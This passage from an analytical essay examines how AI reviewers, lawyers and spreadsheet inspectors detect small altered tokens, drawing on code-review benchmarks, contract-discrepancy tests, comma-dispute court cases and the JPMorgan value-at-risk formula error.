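Models do much better when they see both versions at once. In *TREAT*, a broad evaluation of 26 models on programming tasks, Gao, Li and colleagues (2025) gave each model both functions from a PrimeVul pair and asked it to label each one. GPT-4.1 got 91% of 200 pairs right, GPT-5 got 80% and Claude Sonnet 4 got 73%. When the same models judged single functions from PrimeVul, about half of which were faulty, they were only 60% to 70% accurate.

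We would expect side-by-side comparison to improve accuracy if the text shared by both versions had been dominating the verdicts. A function that looks dangerous looks equally dangerous in both versions, so comparing them cancels out that impression and leaves the difference. The model can also treat one version as probably worse and then only has to pick which. Gemini 2.5 Pro apparently did not do this, since it flagged both versions in 72% of pairs and got 26% of pairs right.

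The high scores may overstate how well the models understood the flaws. Calling the shorter version faulty would probably work well here too. Cichoń and Dmitruk found that rule to be right about nine times in ten, and many of their pairs came from PrimeVul. If the faulty version always came first, a model could also have benefited from a bias toward calling the first version faulty. Gao and colleagues describe no check for either possibility.

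GPT-3.5 had the weakest results, getting 13% of pairs right and reversing 48%. Blind guessing would produce about equal numbers of each, so GPT-3.5 must have been responding to some consistent difference between the versions, or to their order, and misreading it. Stronger models could have read the same cue correctly. Swapping the order of the versions, and testing separately on pairs of equal length, would show how much of the 91% remains.

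## AI reviewers working on whole changes, alone and with people

A model that sees only one function cannot look up what `erealloc` does, but an AI reviewer with tools can. At each step, the reviewer can open another file, search for a function's callers, check when somebody last changed a line, or run the program. At the end, it writes a list of suspected faults instead of a single verdict.

### Reading the project and running the code

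Yang, He and colleagues (2026), in *(When) Should a Software Factory be Lights-off?*, tested such reviewers on 1,000 past changes to 98 open-source projects. Each change had introduced a bug that people later confirmed. Human reviewers had caught half of the bugs before the change was merged and missed the rest. The AI reviewer received the project as it stood at the time, the change, and the author's description of the change, but no hint that anything was wrong. It ranked its findings by severity, and three language models judged whether any of the top five matched the known bug.

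The best model, Claude Opus 5, found 71.9% of the bugs, taking about ten minutes and costing about $3 per change. Claude Opus 4.6, about five months older, found 47.7%. Opus 5 did better on the bugs people had caught (79.6%) than on those they had missed (64.2%).

The reviewers spent 75% of their steps opening and searching files, and only 8% running code. Running code sometimes resolved the question. While reviewing a change to yt-dlp, a program that downloads videos, Opus 5 fetched about 25 archived web pages and ran the new code. It reported that livestream pages produced an identifier in only two of nine cases. A programmer can repeat a test like that much more quickly than they can decide whether to believe an opinion.

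In runs by six leading models, the reviewer opened the file containing the bug 95.6% of the time and reported a problem in that file 80.2% of the time, but identified the bug itself only 56.2% of the time.

Comments in the code sometimes led the models to wrong judgments. In a change to Selenium, a tool for testing websites, a comment and the author's description both explained what a condition was meant to do. The condition did something else, but every model approved it. The models used the comment as evidence that the code was right, when a careful reviewer would have taken the mismatch between them as evidence of an error. Meta's model similarly relied on comments that said a mutant contained a bug.

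Yang and colleagues also looked at which bugs the models tended to miss. The odds of detection were 2.6 times as high when the bug was visible in the diff, and they fell as changes grew larger. The odds were about half as high when the change was a bug fix as when it added a feature. At Chromium OS, by contrast, human reviewers were more likely to catch security defects in bug fixes. Yang and colleagues suggest that the AI reviewers focus on whether the fix works and less on what else it might break.

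The models' bug detection also fell by up to 25.5% on 800 changes from two very large private projects at one company. Only 23% of the bugs there were visible in the diff, compared with 46% in the open-source projects. This suggests that models will miss more bugs at companies with a lot of unwritten knowledge about their own code.

Other tests have produced lower detection rates. *Code Review Agent Benchmark* (2026) found that tools including Claude Code and Codex caught about 40% of the issues human reviewers had raised. *CR-Bench-v2* (Pereira, Sinha and colleagues, 2026) tested nine systems on 174 changes with known bugs, and the best system found about a third of the bugs. Eight of the nine either reviewed the diff in one step or repeatedly revised a first review, and the strongest model any of those eight used was GPT-5.2.

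Newer models, and the inclusion of bugs that people had also caught, probably explain much of the gap between a third and 72%. GPT-5-mini was in both tests and found about the same share of the bugs that the original reviewers had missed. It found 33.7% in the test by Pereira and colleagues, where it revised its own reviews, and 33.4% in the test by Yang and colleagues, where it could explore a whole project. The tests used different projects, so this doesn't show that the tools were useless.

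OpenAI trained an AI code reviewer and reports on its alignment blog that giving the reviewer access to the whole project and the ability to run code improved both its detection rate and its precision. Perhaps a model has to be good enough, or have the right training, before the extra information helps.

### Finding some flaws and judging one change

The tests on whole changes do not penalise false alarms as the pair test does, which helps explain why the detection rate reached 72% when the models that judged single functions got at most about a quarter of the pairs right. Every change contained a bug, so being suspicious could not lower a reviewer's score. Opus 5 listed about six findings per change, and only one had to match the recorded bug. Some of the others may have been real bugs that nobody had recorded, and some were probably wrong.

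An AI can find serious flaws and still be a poor judge of one particular change. Suppose 20 of a project's 10,000 functions contain a serious flaw. An AI reviewer searches them all, demonstrates 5 of the flaws by running the program, and drops every suspicion it cannot demonstrate. This is an excellent result for the developers, who receive five real flaws and no false alarms.

Suppose a developer cares about only one of those functions, and the reviewer reports no flaw in it. Because the reviewer detected only 25% of flaws, the chance that the function is flawed falls only from 0.2% to 0.15%. Although the search succeeded for the project, it gave this developer almost no new information.

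A higher detection rate helps, but the remaining risk can still be too high. If a change has a 10% chance of containing a serious bug, and a reviewer that catches 72% of such bugs reports no real one, the chance is still about 3%. That may be acceptable for the layout of a web page, but not for the line that decides who gets root access.

Demonstrations make this difference larger. They remove false alarms, because a reviewer cannot demonstrate a fault that does not exist. But a reviewer may fail to demonstrate a real fault, especially one that appears for only one rare input. So a successful demonstration is very strong evidence of an error, while a failed attempt is weak evidence that the code is sound.

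### Rejecting correct code

A model that doesn't run the code has no such check on its suspicions. In *Are LLMs Reliable Code Reviewers?*, Jin and Chen (2026) measured how often models reject correct code when they compare it with a written requirement. They took more than 700 short programming exercises from three public collections and paired each requirement with one correct program and one faulty one. Five models judged each program separately, without running it. The researchers asked for the judgment in three ways: a yes or no alone, a verdict with an explanation, and a verdict with an explanation plus a corrected program if the answer was no.

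Rejecting a correct program is a false alarm, and accepting a faulty one is a miss. The table shows results for the largest collection, about 500 exercises. The three figures in each cell are for the verdict alone, the verdict with an explanation, and the verdict with an explanation and a fix.

| Model | Correct programs rejected | Faulty programs accepted |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | 36%, 74%, 88% | 3.7%, 0%, about 0% |
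| Gemini 2.0 Flash | 35%, 35%, 40% | 10.3%, 11.1%, 7.7% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 59%, 56%, 62% | 6.6%, 6.9%, 5.4% |
| Llama 3.1 8B | 75%, 92%, 88% | 3.6%, 0.4%, 1.9% |
| Mistral Small 3.1 | 61%, 48%, 74% | 5.3%, 7.1%, 4.3% |

Even with the simplest question, the models rejected at least a third of the correct programs. Every model rejected more of them when asked for an explanation and a fix. Jin and Chen call this *overcorrection*. It is surprising because people often ask a model to explain itself hoping for a more careful answer.

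When the instructions asked for an explanation and a fix as well as a verdict, Claude Sonnet 4.5 and Gemini needed less evidence before rejecting a program, perhaps because a request for a fix implies that something needs fixing. They did not get noticeably better or worse at telling correct programs from faulty ones. Discriminability (d'), the signal detection measure of that ability, was about 1.3 for Claude Sonnet 4.5 and about 1.7 for Gemini under both sets of instructions.

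The longer instructions changed GPT-4o's verdicts much more. When asked only for a verdict, it wrongly rejected 184 correct programs and wrongly accepted 19 faulty ones. The longer instructions raised the wrong rejections to about 450 and almost eliminated the wrong acceptances. Whether that is worthwhile depends on how much harm a missed error would do. Half of the programs in this test were faulty, and the longer instructions added about 14 wrong rejections for each wrong acceptance they prevented. In ordinary work most programs are correct, so that ratio would be much higher.

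In 48% of 4,190 explanations for rejecting correct programs, the models claimed that the logic was wrong, often without giving an input that would fail. They added a requirement that nobody had stated in another 14%, and claimed an error at a boundary, such as `<` where there should be `<=`, in 13%. So the models do look at the tokens where decisive changes often occur, but they also report errors there when the tokens are correct.

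Models sometimes rejected a faulty program but misdiagnosed the fault. When they rejected programs with a wrong operator, their explanations named the wrong kind of fault in 46% of cases and didn't name any kind in another 7%. A programmer who followed a wrong explanation might change a correct line and leave the faulty one alone.

Jin and Chen also tried to reduce wrong rejections. When a model rejected a program and offered a fix, they ran both versions on the exercise's tests and some extra ones. They reversed the rejection if the original passed and the fix changed nothing or made things worse. Averaged over the five models, wrong rejections in the largest collection fell from 69% to 29%, while wrong acceptances rose slightly.

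The remedy relies on tests that came with the correct answers. A team with such good tests could run them and would have much less need for the model's verdict. The extra tests, which a language model wrote from the requirement, are more like what a real project could have, but Jin and Chen don't report how the remedy does with those alone.

The models in this experiment were not the strongest available in 2026, and the exercises were small. Some of the requirements may also have been vague enough that rejecting the official solution was reasonable. Newer models may well overcorrect less. Before using an AI reviewer to block changes, a team should measure how many correct changes it blocks when given the exact instructions it will have in actual use.

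### The argument for replacing human reviewers

*The End of Code Review* (Monperrus, 2026) argues that AI agents should take over most code review from people. Developers at large organisations spend 10% to 15% of their working hours on review, and a change often waits more than a day for a response. Monperrus argues that human review is good at catching surface problems but unreliable for deeper errors of logic. An AI reviewer can consult the tests, the documentation and the history of every function, and its attention does not fade over time.

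Monperrus is especially critical of the usual compromise, in which an AI writes the code and a person has to approve it. The code looks plausible and passes its tests, and there is more of it than anyone can read properly, so people approve it as a formality. The approval step then adds delay without providing a real check. Monperrus would instead have a second, independent AI review the code, and would keep human approval for high-risk changes, new designs and regulated software that a named person has to answer for.

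The essay contains no new experiment. The experiments on code reading give some support to Monperrus's low opinion of human reviewers, but weak reviewers could be worth keeping if they catch errors that the AI misses. Monperrus also describes AI reviews as instantaneous and deterministic, but the reviews by Opus 5 took about ten minutes each, and Yang and colleagues warn that such agents behave differently from run to run.

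Two of the objections Monperrus discusses matter most for decisive changes. One is that a human reviewer who is unsure will usually say so, while a model may approve the change without comment. Faisal (2026), in *Todoist's AI Code Reviewer Waved Through the Hacker's Data-Theft Code, CEO Admits*, reports the head of the to-do-list company Todoist as saying that in November 2026 its AI reviewer treated an intruder's changes as normal. Those changes were much larger than one token, but nobody had yet told the reviewer to look for data theft. People also need to be told what to look for, as the experiment with the `"MD5"` flaw showed.

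To address silent approvals, Monperrus proposes having several AI reviewers examine each change, requiring them to agree, and training them to admit when they don't know. The other objection applies to these reviewers too. If they come from the same family of models that wrote the code, they may overlook exactly the kind of flaw that the writer tends to produce. Monperrus suggests using specialised security models for the final check.

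Results from Yang and colleagues give a rough idea of how often different models miss the same bugs. Two models from OpenAI and one from Anthropic each found between 47% and 49% of the bugs that human reviewers had missed. If the models' misses had been independent, the three together would have found about 86%. A system that combined reviews from these models found only 53%, and combining three reviews by a single model did about as well.

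The agent that merged the reviews may have caused part of the shortfall by discarding correct findings. Some overlap is also inevitable, because some bugs are harder than others for any reviewer. But the result suggests that using models from different companies adds much less independence than one might expect.

Requiring every reviewer to approve would also cause more false alarms. In the smaller of Jin and Chen's two main collections, GPT-4o and Claude Sonnet 4.5 each rejected 26% of correct programs when asked only for a verdict. If three such reviewers made their mistakes independently, at least one would object to about 60% of correct programs. If their mistakes overlapped, there would be fewer false alarms, but the second and third reviewers would probably catch fewer of the errors the first one missed.

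Yang and colleagues conclude that AI review without people is suitable only for narrow, low-stakes changes. This is closer to Monperrus's position than the title of his essay suggests, since both would have people review the important changes. For high-sensitivity outputs, it is hard to tell which changes are important, because replacing one comparison with another looks routine until someone works out what it does.

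### What people and AI reviewers achieve together

People and AI reviewers seem to notice somewhat different things. In data from Yang and colleagues, people were relatively better at catching code that would be hard to maintain, while AI reviewers were relatively better at catching severe bugs and reliability problems. The human reviewers caught 50% of the bugs, and adding the top five findings from Opus 5 raised the total to 82.1%.

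That total is the 50% that people had caught plus 64.2% of the other 50%. Nobody reviewed the code with the AI's help. Adding the two assumes that people would still find everything they found alone, and would recognise and act on every correct finding from the AI. The total also leaves out bugs that nobody has discovered yet.

A controlled study that Yang and colleagues summarise gives reason to doubt the first assumption. Expert developers who received an AI-written review focused on the issues it raised. They found more minor problems but no additional serious ones, and they did not save time or feel more confident. An AI reviewer may therefore replace some of a person's own search instead of adding to it.

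Companies can easily miss this effect if they judge a reviewer by whether people like it. Trębacz (2025) reports in *A Practical Approach to Verifying Code at Scale* that OpenAI uses AI to review all of its internal code changes and that more than 80% of developers' reactions are positive. In the same talk, Trębacz warns that developers may come to rely on the reviewer too much. A reviewer can also make useful comments and still miss most bugs. In the test by Pereira and colleagues, AI judges rated 78% of the comments from Google's Gemini Code Assist as useful, but it found only 8.1% of the known bugs.

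Trust in the AI that writes the code can be a larger problem. In *Coding With "Enemy"* (2026), 94% of the developers who spent about five hours working with a sabotaging coding agent did not detect the sabotage.

### Auditing machine-learning research

A failed test or a crash often reveals an error in software. An error in a research project may change only the conclusion, which nobody can recognise as wrong without knowing the right one. A 2026 benchmark of nine machine-learning projects tested whether AI models, and people with AI help, could detect errors of this kind that had been planted deliberately.

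The auditors received a paper and its code. There was a 50% chance that somebody had altered the project so that its main finding changed. The auditors estimated the probability of this and ranked up to five proposed corrections. The human auditors had two hours, could use language models, and also received an audit by GPT-5.2.

The benchmark scored the probabilities by *AUROC* (area under the receiver operating characteristic curve), the chance that an auditor gives a randomly chosen altered project a higher probability than a randomly chosen honest one. Guessing scores 0.5 and perfect separation scores 1.

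| Auditor | AUROC | First correction right | One of five corrections right |
|---|---|---|---|
| Gemini 3.1 Pro, the best model | 0.77 | 42% | 53% |
| People with AI help | 0.68 | 38% | 54% |

AUROC does not depend on where an auditor puts the threshold for raising an alarm. If the impressions of honest and altered projects follow bell curves of equal width, it is related to discriminability by

$$\text{AUROC} = \Phi\!\left(\frac{d'}{\sqrt{2}}\right)$$

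where Φ reverses the function z, turning a distance on the bell curve back into a proportion. An AUROC of 0.77 then corresponds to a d' of about 1.0, and 0.68 to about 0.7. To catch 80% of the altered projects, the best model would have to raise a false alarm on about 42% of the honest ones. If only 1% of projects were altered, about 2% of its alarms would be right.

The result is more encouraging for single wrong tokens. A wrong operator is normally an error of logic, meaning a formal mistake in the code or mathematics. For errors of this kind, Gemini 3.1 Pro almost always had the right correction among its five. Pointing to the place of the error is called *localization*, and it is more useful to a programmer than a bare warning.

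Errors in experimental design were much harder. For four of them, each auditor's five proposed corrections included the right one less than 20% of the time. Auditors often noticed something odd but could not tell whether it was a reasonable choice. The benchmark's creator thinks omissions are the hardest, because the auditor has to notice that something is missing. Human code reviewers have a similar weakness. At Chromium OS, they missed most of the absent input checks.

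Honest projects also contained harmless bugs and strange choices that made the auditors suspicious. Gemini 3.1 Pro objected to nearly everything and often gave probabilities above 90%. Claude Opus 4.6 usually stayed below 50%, even when it had proposed the right correction. Someone who looked only at Claude's probabilities would have passed projects in which it had already found the error.

With nine projects, the difference between 0.77 and 0.68 could easily be chance, so the benchmark does not establish that the best model is better than people with AI help. Each model was also fairly consistent in how suspicious it was, but one person's 60% could express less suspicion than another person's 40%. Pooling people's answers therefore lowers the human AUROC even if each person ranks the projects reasonably well.

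## Altered words in contracts

Nobody can test a contract by running it, as a programmer can with a program. The parties may follow it for years without finding out that they understand a clause differently. If they dispute the clause, a judge or regulator decides what it means, and the decision can depend on one word.

A contract is correct if it records what the parties agreed, so an altered clause can be clear, lawful and normal but still wrong. These invented examples show the kinds of token a reviewer has most reason to check.

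| Kind of token | Agreed wording | Altered wording | Effect |
|---|---|---|---|
| Negation | The tenant may not sublet | The tenant may sublet | A ban becomes a permission |
| "And" or "or" | If the buyer pays late and ignores a warning | If the buyer pays late or ignores a warning | One failure is enough |
| "Shall" or "may" | The insurer shall repair the car | The insurer may repair the car | A duty becomes a choice |
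| Defined term | Losses of the Group | Losses of the Company | Subsidiaries lose their cover |
| Cross-reference | Subject to clause 12 | Subject to clause 13 | A different exception applies |
| Amount | Liability up to £1,000,000 | Liability up to £100,000 | The limit falls by 90% |
| Date | Notice before 1 March | Notice before 1 May | The deadline moves by two months |

A defined term is a word, usually capitalized, that the contract gives its own meaning. A reader has to look up the definitions to see how "Group" and "Company" differ. Punctuation can matter too, as two well-known disputes show.

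### The comma in the Rogers contract

In 2002 the Canadian cable company Rogers agreed to pay the telephone company Aliant $9.60 a year for each pole that carried its cables. The agreement was to run for five years, until 31 May 2007, and then for further five-year terms, "unless and until terminated by one year prior notice in writing" from either side. In January 2005 Aliant gave a year's notice. Rogers objected that neither side could end the agreement before the first five years had passed.

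In July 2006 Canada's telecommunications regulator, the CRTC (2006), ruled that Aliant could end its pole agreement with Rogers at any time with a year's notice. It reasoned that a comma just before "unless" made the notice provision apply to the first five years as well as to the renewals. Many of the poles belonged to a power company, which wanted about twice the old price. Rogers put its extra cost at about $700,000, according to the trade publication Cartt.ca, although early reports had put it at over $2 million.

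Accounts of the million-dollar comma often leave out that Rogers asked the regulator to reconsider and produced the French version of the agreement. The regulator had approved the standard wording in both languages in 2000, and the French version plainly allows notice only a year before the contract expires. Aliant replied that the French version was irrelevant because the parties had signed the English one.

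The regulator sided with Rogers in its second decision, CRTC (2007). It had imposed the standard wording itself, so it had to determine what it had meant, and the English and French versions were equally good evidence of that. The English text could be read in two ways, but the French text supported only one of them. The agreement had therefore lasted until 31 May 2007. The regulator did not need to decide whether its earlier rule about commas was right.

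The French version stated the same fact a second time, like the amount in words on a cheque. Rogers still did not get everything it wanted, because the regulator also found that it had no authority over the power company's poles and so could not enforce the old price for them.

### The missing comma in Maine

A comma was also at issue, this time in a statute, in *O'Connor v. Oakhurst Dairy* (2017), decided by the First Circuit, the federal appeals court that covers Maine. Maine law denied overtime pay to people who did certain work with food, listed as "canning, processing, preserving, freezing, drying, marketing, storing, packing for shipment or distribution". The dairy's drivers distributed milk but did not pack it, so they had a right to overtime if the law meant packing for either shipment or distribution, but not if "distribution" was a separate item in the list.

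A comma after "shipment" would have settled the matter in the dairy's favour. Without one, both sides had respectable arguments. The dairy pointed out that a list normally has "or" before its last item, and there was no "or" before "packing". The drivers pointed out that every activity on the list ended in "-ing" except the disputed one. Maine's law-drafting manual had a rule against the comma before the last item, which helped the dairy, but it also included a caution to take care when an item had a modifier.

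The court found the wording ambiguous even after considering the law's purpose and history. Maine's courts interpret ambiguous wage laws to best serve their protective purpose, so the drivers won. The dairy later agreed to pay $5 million, which more than 120 drivers were eligible to share (Maine Public, *Maine Dairy Drivers Settle Overtime Case That Hinged On An Absent Comma*, 2018).

A reviewer who checked the sentence against the drafting manual might well have passed it, since leaving out the comma was the house style. The reviewer had to notice that the sentence had a second reading to see the problem. Maine's legislature has since replaced the commas with semicolons, according to CNN (2018). The new wording, which the Australian broadcaster SBS quotes, also changes "distribution" to "distributing", so the drivers' argument about "-ing" would no longer work either.

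### What a redline catches

Lawyers call a diff of two drafts a *redline*. Suppose two companies agree on the wording of a contract on Monday, and on Friday one sends the other a copy to sign. A redline of the two versions shows every word that differs. If the only difference is that "shall" has become "may", the reviewer only has to consider that word and can ask who approved the change, as with a change to a program.

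A word processor's redline can omit edits if someone forgets to turn on change tracking, or accepts an edit and so removes its mark. Comparing the new file with a saved copy of the agreed draft is safer because it does not depend on what the other side recorded.

An incomplete record may be worse than none. Shah, Kakade and Patel (2026), in *What Do LLM Judges Actually Verify?*, asked AI models whether an answer cited technical standards for the internet that newer ones had replaced. With a complete list of replacements, the models caught nearly every outdated citation. The researchers then deleted some entries from the list and looked at the 24 faults that those entries would have revealed.

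| Model | Caught from the texts alone | Caught with the incomplete list |
|---|---|---|
| Gemini 3.1 Pro | 23 | 1 |
| GPT-5.5 | 23 | 9 |
| Claude Opus 4.5 | 17 | 9 |
| Gemma 4 26B | 13 | 0 |

The models evidently took an omission from the list as a sign that nothing was wrong. Lawyers could easily make the same mistake with tracked changes, though nobody has shown that they do. A reviewer who receives a document with three marked edits is likely to read those closely and skim the rest.

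Sometimes there is no trusted earlier draft, for instance when the other side writes the first version. *LLMs in Interpreting Legal Documents* (Corbo, 2026) describes checking the contract against a template instead. This will find unusual wording, but most unusual wording is intentional, so precision will be low, as it would have been for the XZ release files.

The agreed draft may also contain an error already, in which case the redline won't show it. This seems to be common. Canadian Lawyer's *Analysis of over 3,000 contracts finds 60 percent had drafting errors* reports research by Spellbook, which has an interest in finding errors because it sells software for reviewing contracts. Many of the errors will also have been harmless, but even if the figure were much lower, a redline that shows no changes would be weak evidence that the contract is correct.

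### The CLAUSE benchmark

When there is nothing reliable to compare a contract with, the reviewer has to find the error by reading. *Better Call CLAUSE* (Roy Choudhury, Chandramouli and colleagues, 2025) tested how well language models do this. It started with two collections of real contracts, CUAD (about 510 commercial agreements) and ContractNLI (about 607 contracts, mostly confidentiality agreements). From these it produced more than 7,500 altered contracts, with about 24,000 alterations in total.

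A language model, Gemini 2.0 Flash, wrote the alterations. There were five basic types:

- ambiguity, such as vague wording or two definitions of one term
- omission of necessary information
- inconsistent use of legal or defined terms
- structural flaws, such as a broken cross-reference
- direct inconsistency, such as a duty to keep data for five years and a duty to delete it within two

Each type had two forms, one that conflicted with another part of the contract and one that conflicted with the law, for ten kinds in all. Many alterations are much larger than one token. One example in the instructions to Gemini replaces "shall comply" with "should make reasonable efforts to comply" and rewrites the sentences that follow.

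A second model then examined each alteration beside the related clauses or the relevant law, and the researchers kept only those it classified as real contradictions. A legal expert confirmed that the ten kinds were realistic, and three specialists in language processing checked a sample and accepted 98.6% of it. The sample's size is unclear because the paper gives it both as 25% of the dataset and as 13,275 alterations, which is more than half of the 24,000.

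In the first task, the models answered yes or no to whether a contract contained any discrepancy. About half of the contracts were unaltered. These are the results on the CUAD contracts for one typical kind of alteration, ambiguous wording that conflicts with a law. The paper does not give the last column directly, but it can be calculated from the accuracy, precision and detection rate.

| Model | Precision | Altered contracts flagged | Unaltered contracts flagged |
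|---|---|---|---|
| Gemini 2.5 Flash | 49% | 92% | about 95% |
| Gemini 2.0 Flash | 50% | 77% | about 74% |
| Llama 3.3 70B | 44% | 69% | about 88% |
| GPT-4o-mini | 36% | 48% | about 82% |

Gemini 2.5 Flash had the highest F1, but only because it flagged nearly every contract. Its precision was therefore the share of contracts that contained an alteration. Gemini 2.0 Flash did barely better than blind guessing.

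The other two models, GPT-4o-mini and Llama, flagged the unaltered contracts much more often than the altered ones, so they must have been responding wrongly to some difference between the two groups, perhaps one unrelated to the errors.

The labels may also be part of the problem, because the test counts every flag on an unaltered contract as a false alarm, and real contracts contain errors of their own. If around 60% of them do, a perfect reviewer would answer "yes" to many of the originals and be marked wrong. The yes-or-no scores are therefore poor evidence of how well these models read contracts, although they do show that a 92% detection rate was no reason to trust a model.

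In the second task, the models saw only altered contracts and had to decide whether each one contradicted itself, contradicted the law, or did neither. "Neither" was never correct, so a model could score about 50% by always choosing the same one of the other two answers. On CUAD, the models were right between 47% and 64% of the time, with most scores close to 50%. The best score on the other collection was 73%.

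The third task is closer to what a lawyer needs. The models had to quote every faulty passage, explain what was wrong with it and, where relevant, name the law it broke. A quotation counted as a match if it shared at least one sentence with the altered passage. On a standard measure of shared wording, the models averaged between 61% and 75%, with Gemini 2.0 Flash scoring highest. Quotations at this level of accuracy would direct a lawyer to roughly the right paragraph, but they do not show that the model identified the word that mattered.

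Giving the models one worked example made them miss fewer alterations and raise more false alarms. We would expect this if the example lowered their threshold for flagging an alteration, although it may also have taught them something.

Two AI judges scored the models' explanations from 0 to 5, and the averages were around 4 for clarity but only 1.4 to 2.6 for completeness. Even the best model named the right law less than 14% of the time, so a lawyer who judged the explanations by how well they were written would have trusted them far too much.

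### Newer models and lawyers

All four models in CLAUSE are now old. *ContractScrub*, a 2026 benchmark, tests newer ones on the last check that lawyers make before the parties sign. Experienced lawyers prepared the contracts, and the errors include misused defined terms, wrong references and inconsistent language. Only one leading model had an average detection rate above 60%.

The strongest models of autumn 2026 came out after the benchmark and may well do better, but an AI reviewer cannot check a contract by running it.

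No published test appears to measure how many altered words lawyers miss, and the nearest results cover broader skills. Legal Futures' *AI beats average legal mind but not best-performing lawyers* reports that a software company compared its software with 20 American lawyers in 2018 on reviewing five confidentiality agreements. The lawyers averaged 85% accuracy and the software scored 94%, but the software did not beat the best lawyers.

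LawNext's *Legal AI tools show promise in first of its kind benchmark study* (2025) reports a later test in which lawyers scored 79.7% on redlining, higher than any of the AI tools. Redlining in that test meant proposing edits to a contract, and someone can be good at that without being good at noticing a missing "not".

### How much the rest of the contract reveals

Contracts have an advantage over many other texts in that their clauses depend on one another. Arbel and Hoffman (2026) measured this dependence in *Generative Gap Filling* by hiding a negotiated term in real contracts and asking readers to predict it from the remaining text. Ordinary people were right about half the time, twice as often as chance. Experienced lawyers were right 59% of the time and language models 88%.

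A reader who can predict a term may notice when the wrong one is in its place. The experiment did not test this, and there is reason to expect a success rate below 88%. Arbel and Hoffman estimate that about two-thirds of the models' success came from information about what such deals usually contain, and only one-third from the wording of the particular contract. The models were nearly perfect when the hidden term was commercially normal, but only about 60% accurate when the parties had chosen something unusual.

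A reviewer who judges a contract by what is normal will tend to catch changes that make it unusual. If a company negotiated an unusually long warranty but the final copy contains the standard one, the error looks more natural than the correct term. The reviewer may also object to the long warranty when it is correct.

### When a court will correct the wording

Judges read a clause as part of the whole contract and can correct some mistakes in two main ways, so a wrong word does not always decide the outcome.

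Interpretation is one way courts can correct an altered word. In *Chartbrook v Persimmon* (2009), the House of Lords, then Britain's highest court, departed from the literal wording of a payment formula. English judges will do this if it is clear both that something has gone wrong with the language and what the parties must have meant. The loan agreement whose 45% rate contradicts its own interest charge would be a good candidate for such a correction. If the rest of the agreement also fits 4.5%, a judge can be confident about which figure to correct.

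The clause about late delivery is a harder case. If the "not" disappears from "the supplier shall not be liable", the result is still a sensible promise by the supplier. With no obvious error in the text, a judge has no reason to restore the word.

The supplier would need the other remedy, which English lawyers call *rectification* and American lawyers call *reformation*. Under it, the court changes the document to match what the parties actually agreed. It is available when both sides meant the same thing but wrote down something else by mistake. It can also be available when only one side was mistaken, if the other knew and kept quiet or caused the mistake by deceit. A party cannot use it to escape a bad bargain, and a court may refuse it if an innocent third party has since relied on the document.

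In *Hand v. Dayton-Hudson*, an American appeal decided in 1985, a company had dismissed one of its lawyers and offered him money to give up any claims against it. He deliberately changed the agreement to preserve some of his claims and returned a version that looked the same as the original. The company's representative signed it without noticing the change. The appeals court upheld a decision to restore the original terms.

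The company could show what the original terms were because it had written them. Without such proof the remedy is hard to get, since American courts generally require clear and convincing evidence, a higher standard than "more likely than not". For the supplier, that would mean an earlier draft with the "not" in it, or emails in which both sides discussed the exclusion. The saved draft would be the best evidence, but the supplier would have to pay for a lawsuit to restore the word, when comparing the draft with the contract before signing would have exposed the change.

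## Altered numbers and formulas in spreadsheets, papers and data pipelines

A wrong number in a spreadsheet is harder to notice than a missing "not" in a sentence, because it looks like any other number and the formula behind it is usually hidden until somebody clicks the cell. The error can pass through many later calculations before it reaches a figure that anyone reads.

### The JPMorgan risk spreadsheet

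In 2012 the American bank JPMorgan lost $6.2 billion, according to Fortune's *Damn Excel* (2013), on trades in credit default swaps, which pay out if a borrower fails to repay. The bank limited its traders' risk using *value at risk*, an estimate of how much a set of investments could lose in a given period, excluding the very worst cases. If the one-day value at risk is $100 million at the 95% level, the bank expects to lose more than that on about one day in 20.

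Kwak (2013) writes in *The Importance of Excel* that the office behind the trades needed a new model for this calculation and gave the job to a mathematician in London. The bank's internal task force later found several errors in the model. The blog Rik Green Investor Forum (2013) quotes the task force on the most significant one, which was in the calculation of how much certain rates had changed. After subtracting the old rate from the new one, the spreadsheet "divided by their sum instead of their average".

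In a spreadsheet, that can be a difference of one word. With the old rate in cell A2 and the new rate in B2, the intended formula and the faulty one might look like this:

```
= (B2 - A2) / AVERAGE(A2, B2)
= (B2 - A2) / SUM(A2, B2)
```

Suppose a rate rises from 2.0 to 2.2. The first formula divides the change of 0.2 by the average of the two rates, 2.1, and gives 9.5%. The second divides it by their sum, 4.2, and gives 4.8%. Both figures are believable. Anyone who does the division in their head will see that 4.8% is too low, but hardly anyone does that for a long column of results.

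The sum of two numbers is twice their average, so the error halved every change and therefore halved the volatility, which measures how widely the changes vary. Campbell (2016), in *How to Keep Your Spreadsheets Out of the Headlines*, an article for the Society of Actuaries, says that this led to a significant understatement of the trading risk. This does not show that the error caused the loss, because the traders chose their positions and nobody can say for certain what they would have done if the figures had been twice as high.

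The blog's author focuses more on why the error lasted. The bank had treated an earlier error as a one-off when it should have looked for others. The author thinks the bank did not want to doubt a model that gave the traders a better answer. The employee who ran the model also reported to its creator.

That explanation is speculative, but it suggests that errors tend to survive when the people they affect have little reason to look for them. If the formula had doubled the estimated risk instead of halving it, the traders would have had a strong reason to look for the mistake.

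Fortune also describes a spreadsheet error behind a 2010 finding by the Harvard economists Carmen Reinhart and Kenneth Rogoff, who reported that economic growth slows dramatically once a country's debt reaches 90% of its annual output. Their spreadsheet left out the first five countries in their data, including Australia and Canada. Three economists at the University of Massachusetts Amherst put the average growth of the most indebted countries at 2.2% a year instead of −0.1%. The missing rows explain only part of the gap, because the critics also objected to other choices, which Reinhart and Rogoff defended.

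Such an omission can be as small as the JPMorgan error. Changing `AVERAGE(B2:B21)` to `AVERAGE(B7:B21)` drops five of the 20 countries, and both formulas give a believable growth rate.

### How many planted errors people find

In *Applying Code Inspection to Spreadsheet Testing*, Panko (1999) asked 60 information systems students to inspect a spreadsheet containing eight planted errors. They first worked alone and found 63% of the errors on average. They then inspected the spreadsheet again in 20 groups of three, and the groups found 83%.

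That is less than three independent readers should find. If each has a 37% chance of missing an error, all three will miss it about 5% of the time (0.37^3), so together they should find about 95% of errors.

The meetings contributed little to the shortfall. They turned up no new errors, and only one group dropped an error that a member had found earlier, out of 160 possible finds (20 groups times eight errors). The 83% is therefore very nearly the share of errors that at least one member had found alone.

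The most likely reason is that some errors are hard for everyone to find. Suppose that readers find four of the eight errors 96% of the time and the other four 30% of the time, so the average is still 63%. Three readers together would find nearly all of the first four but only 1 − 0.70^3, or 66%, of the others, which makes 83% overall. These two rates are only an illustration, but Panko did find that certain types of error were especially hard to detect and that pooling helped most with those.

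Differences between the students could produce the same gap only if the good inspectors tended to end up in the same groups. If the groups formed at random, a careless student was as likely to be grouped with careful students as with careless ones, and the average chance that all three missed a given error would still be about 5%.

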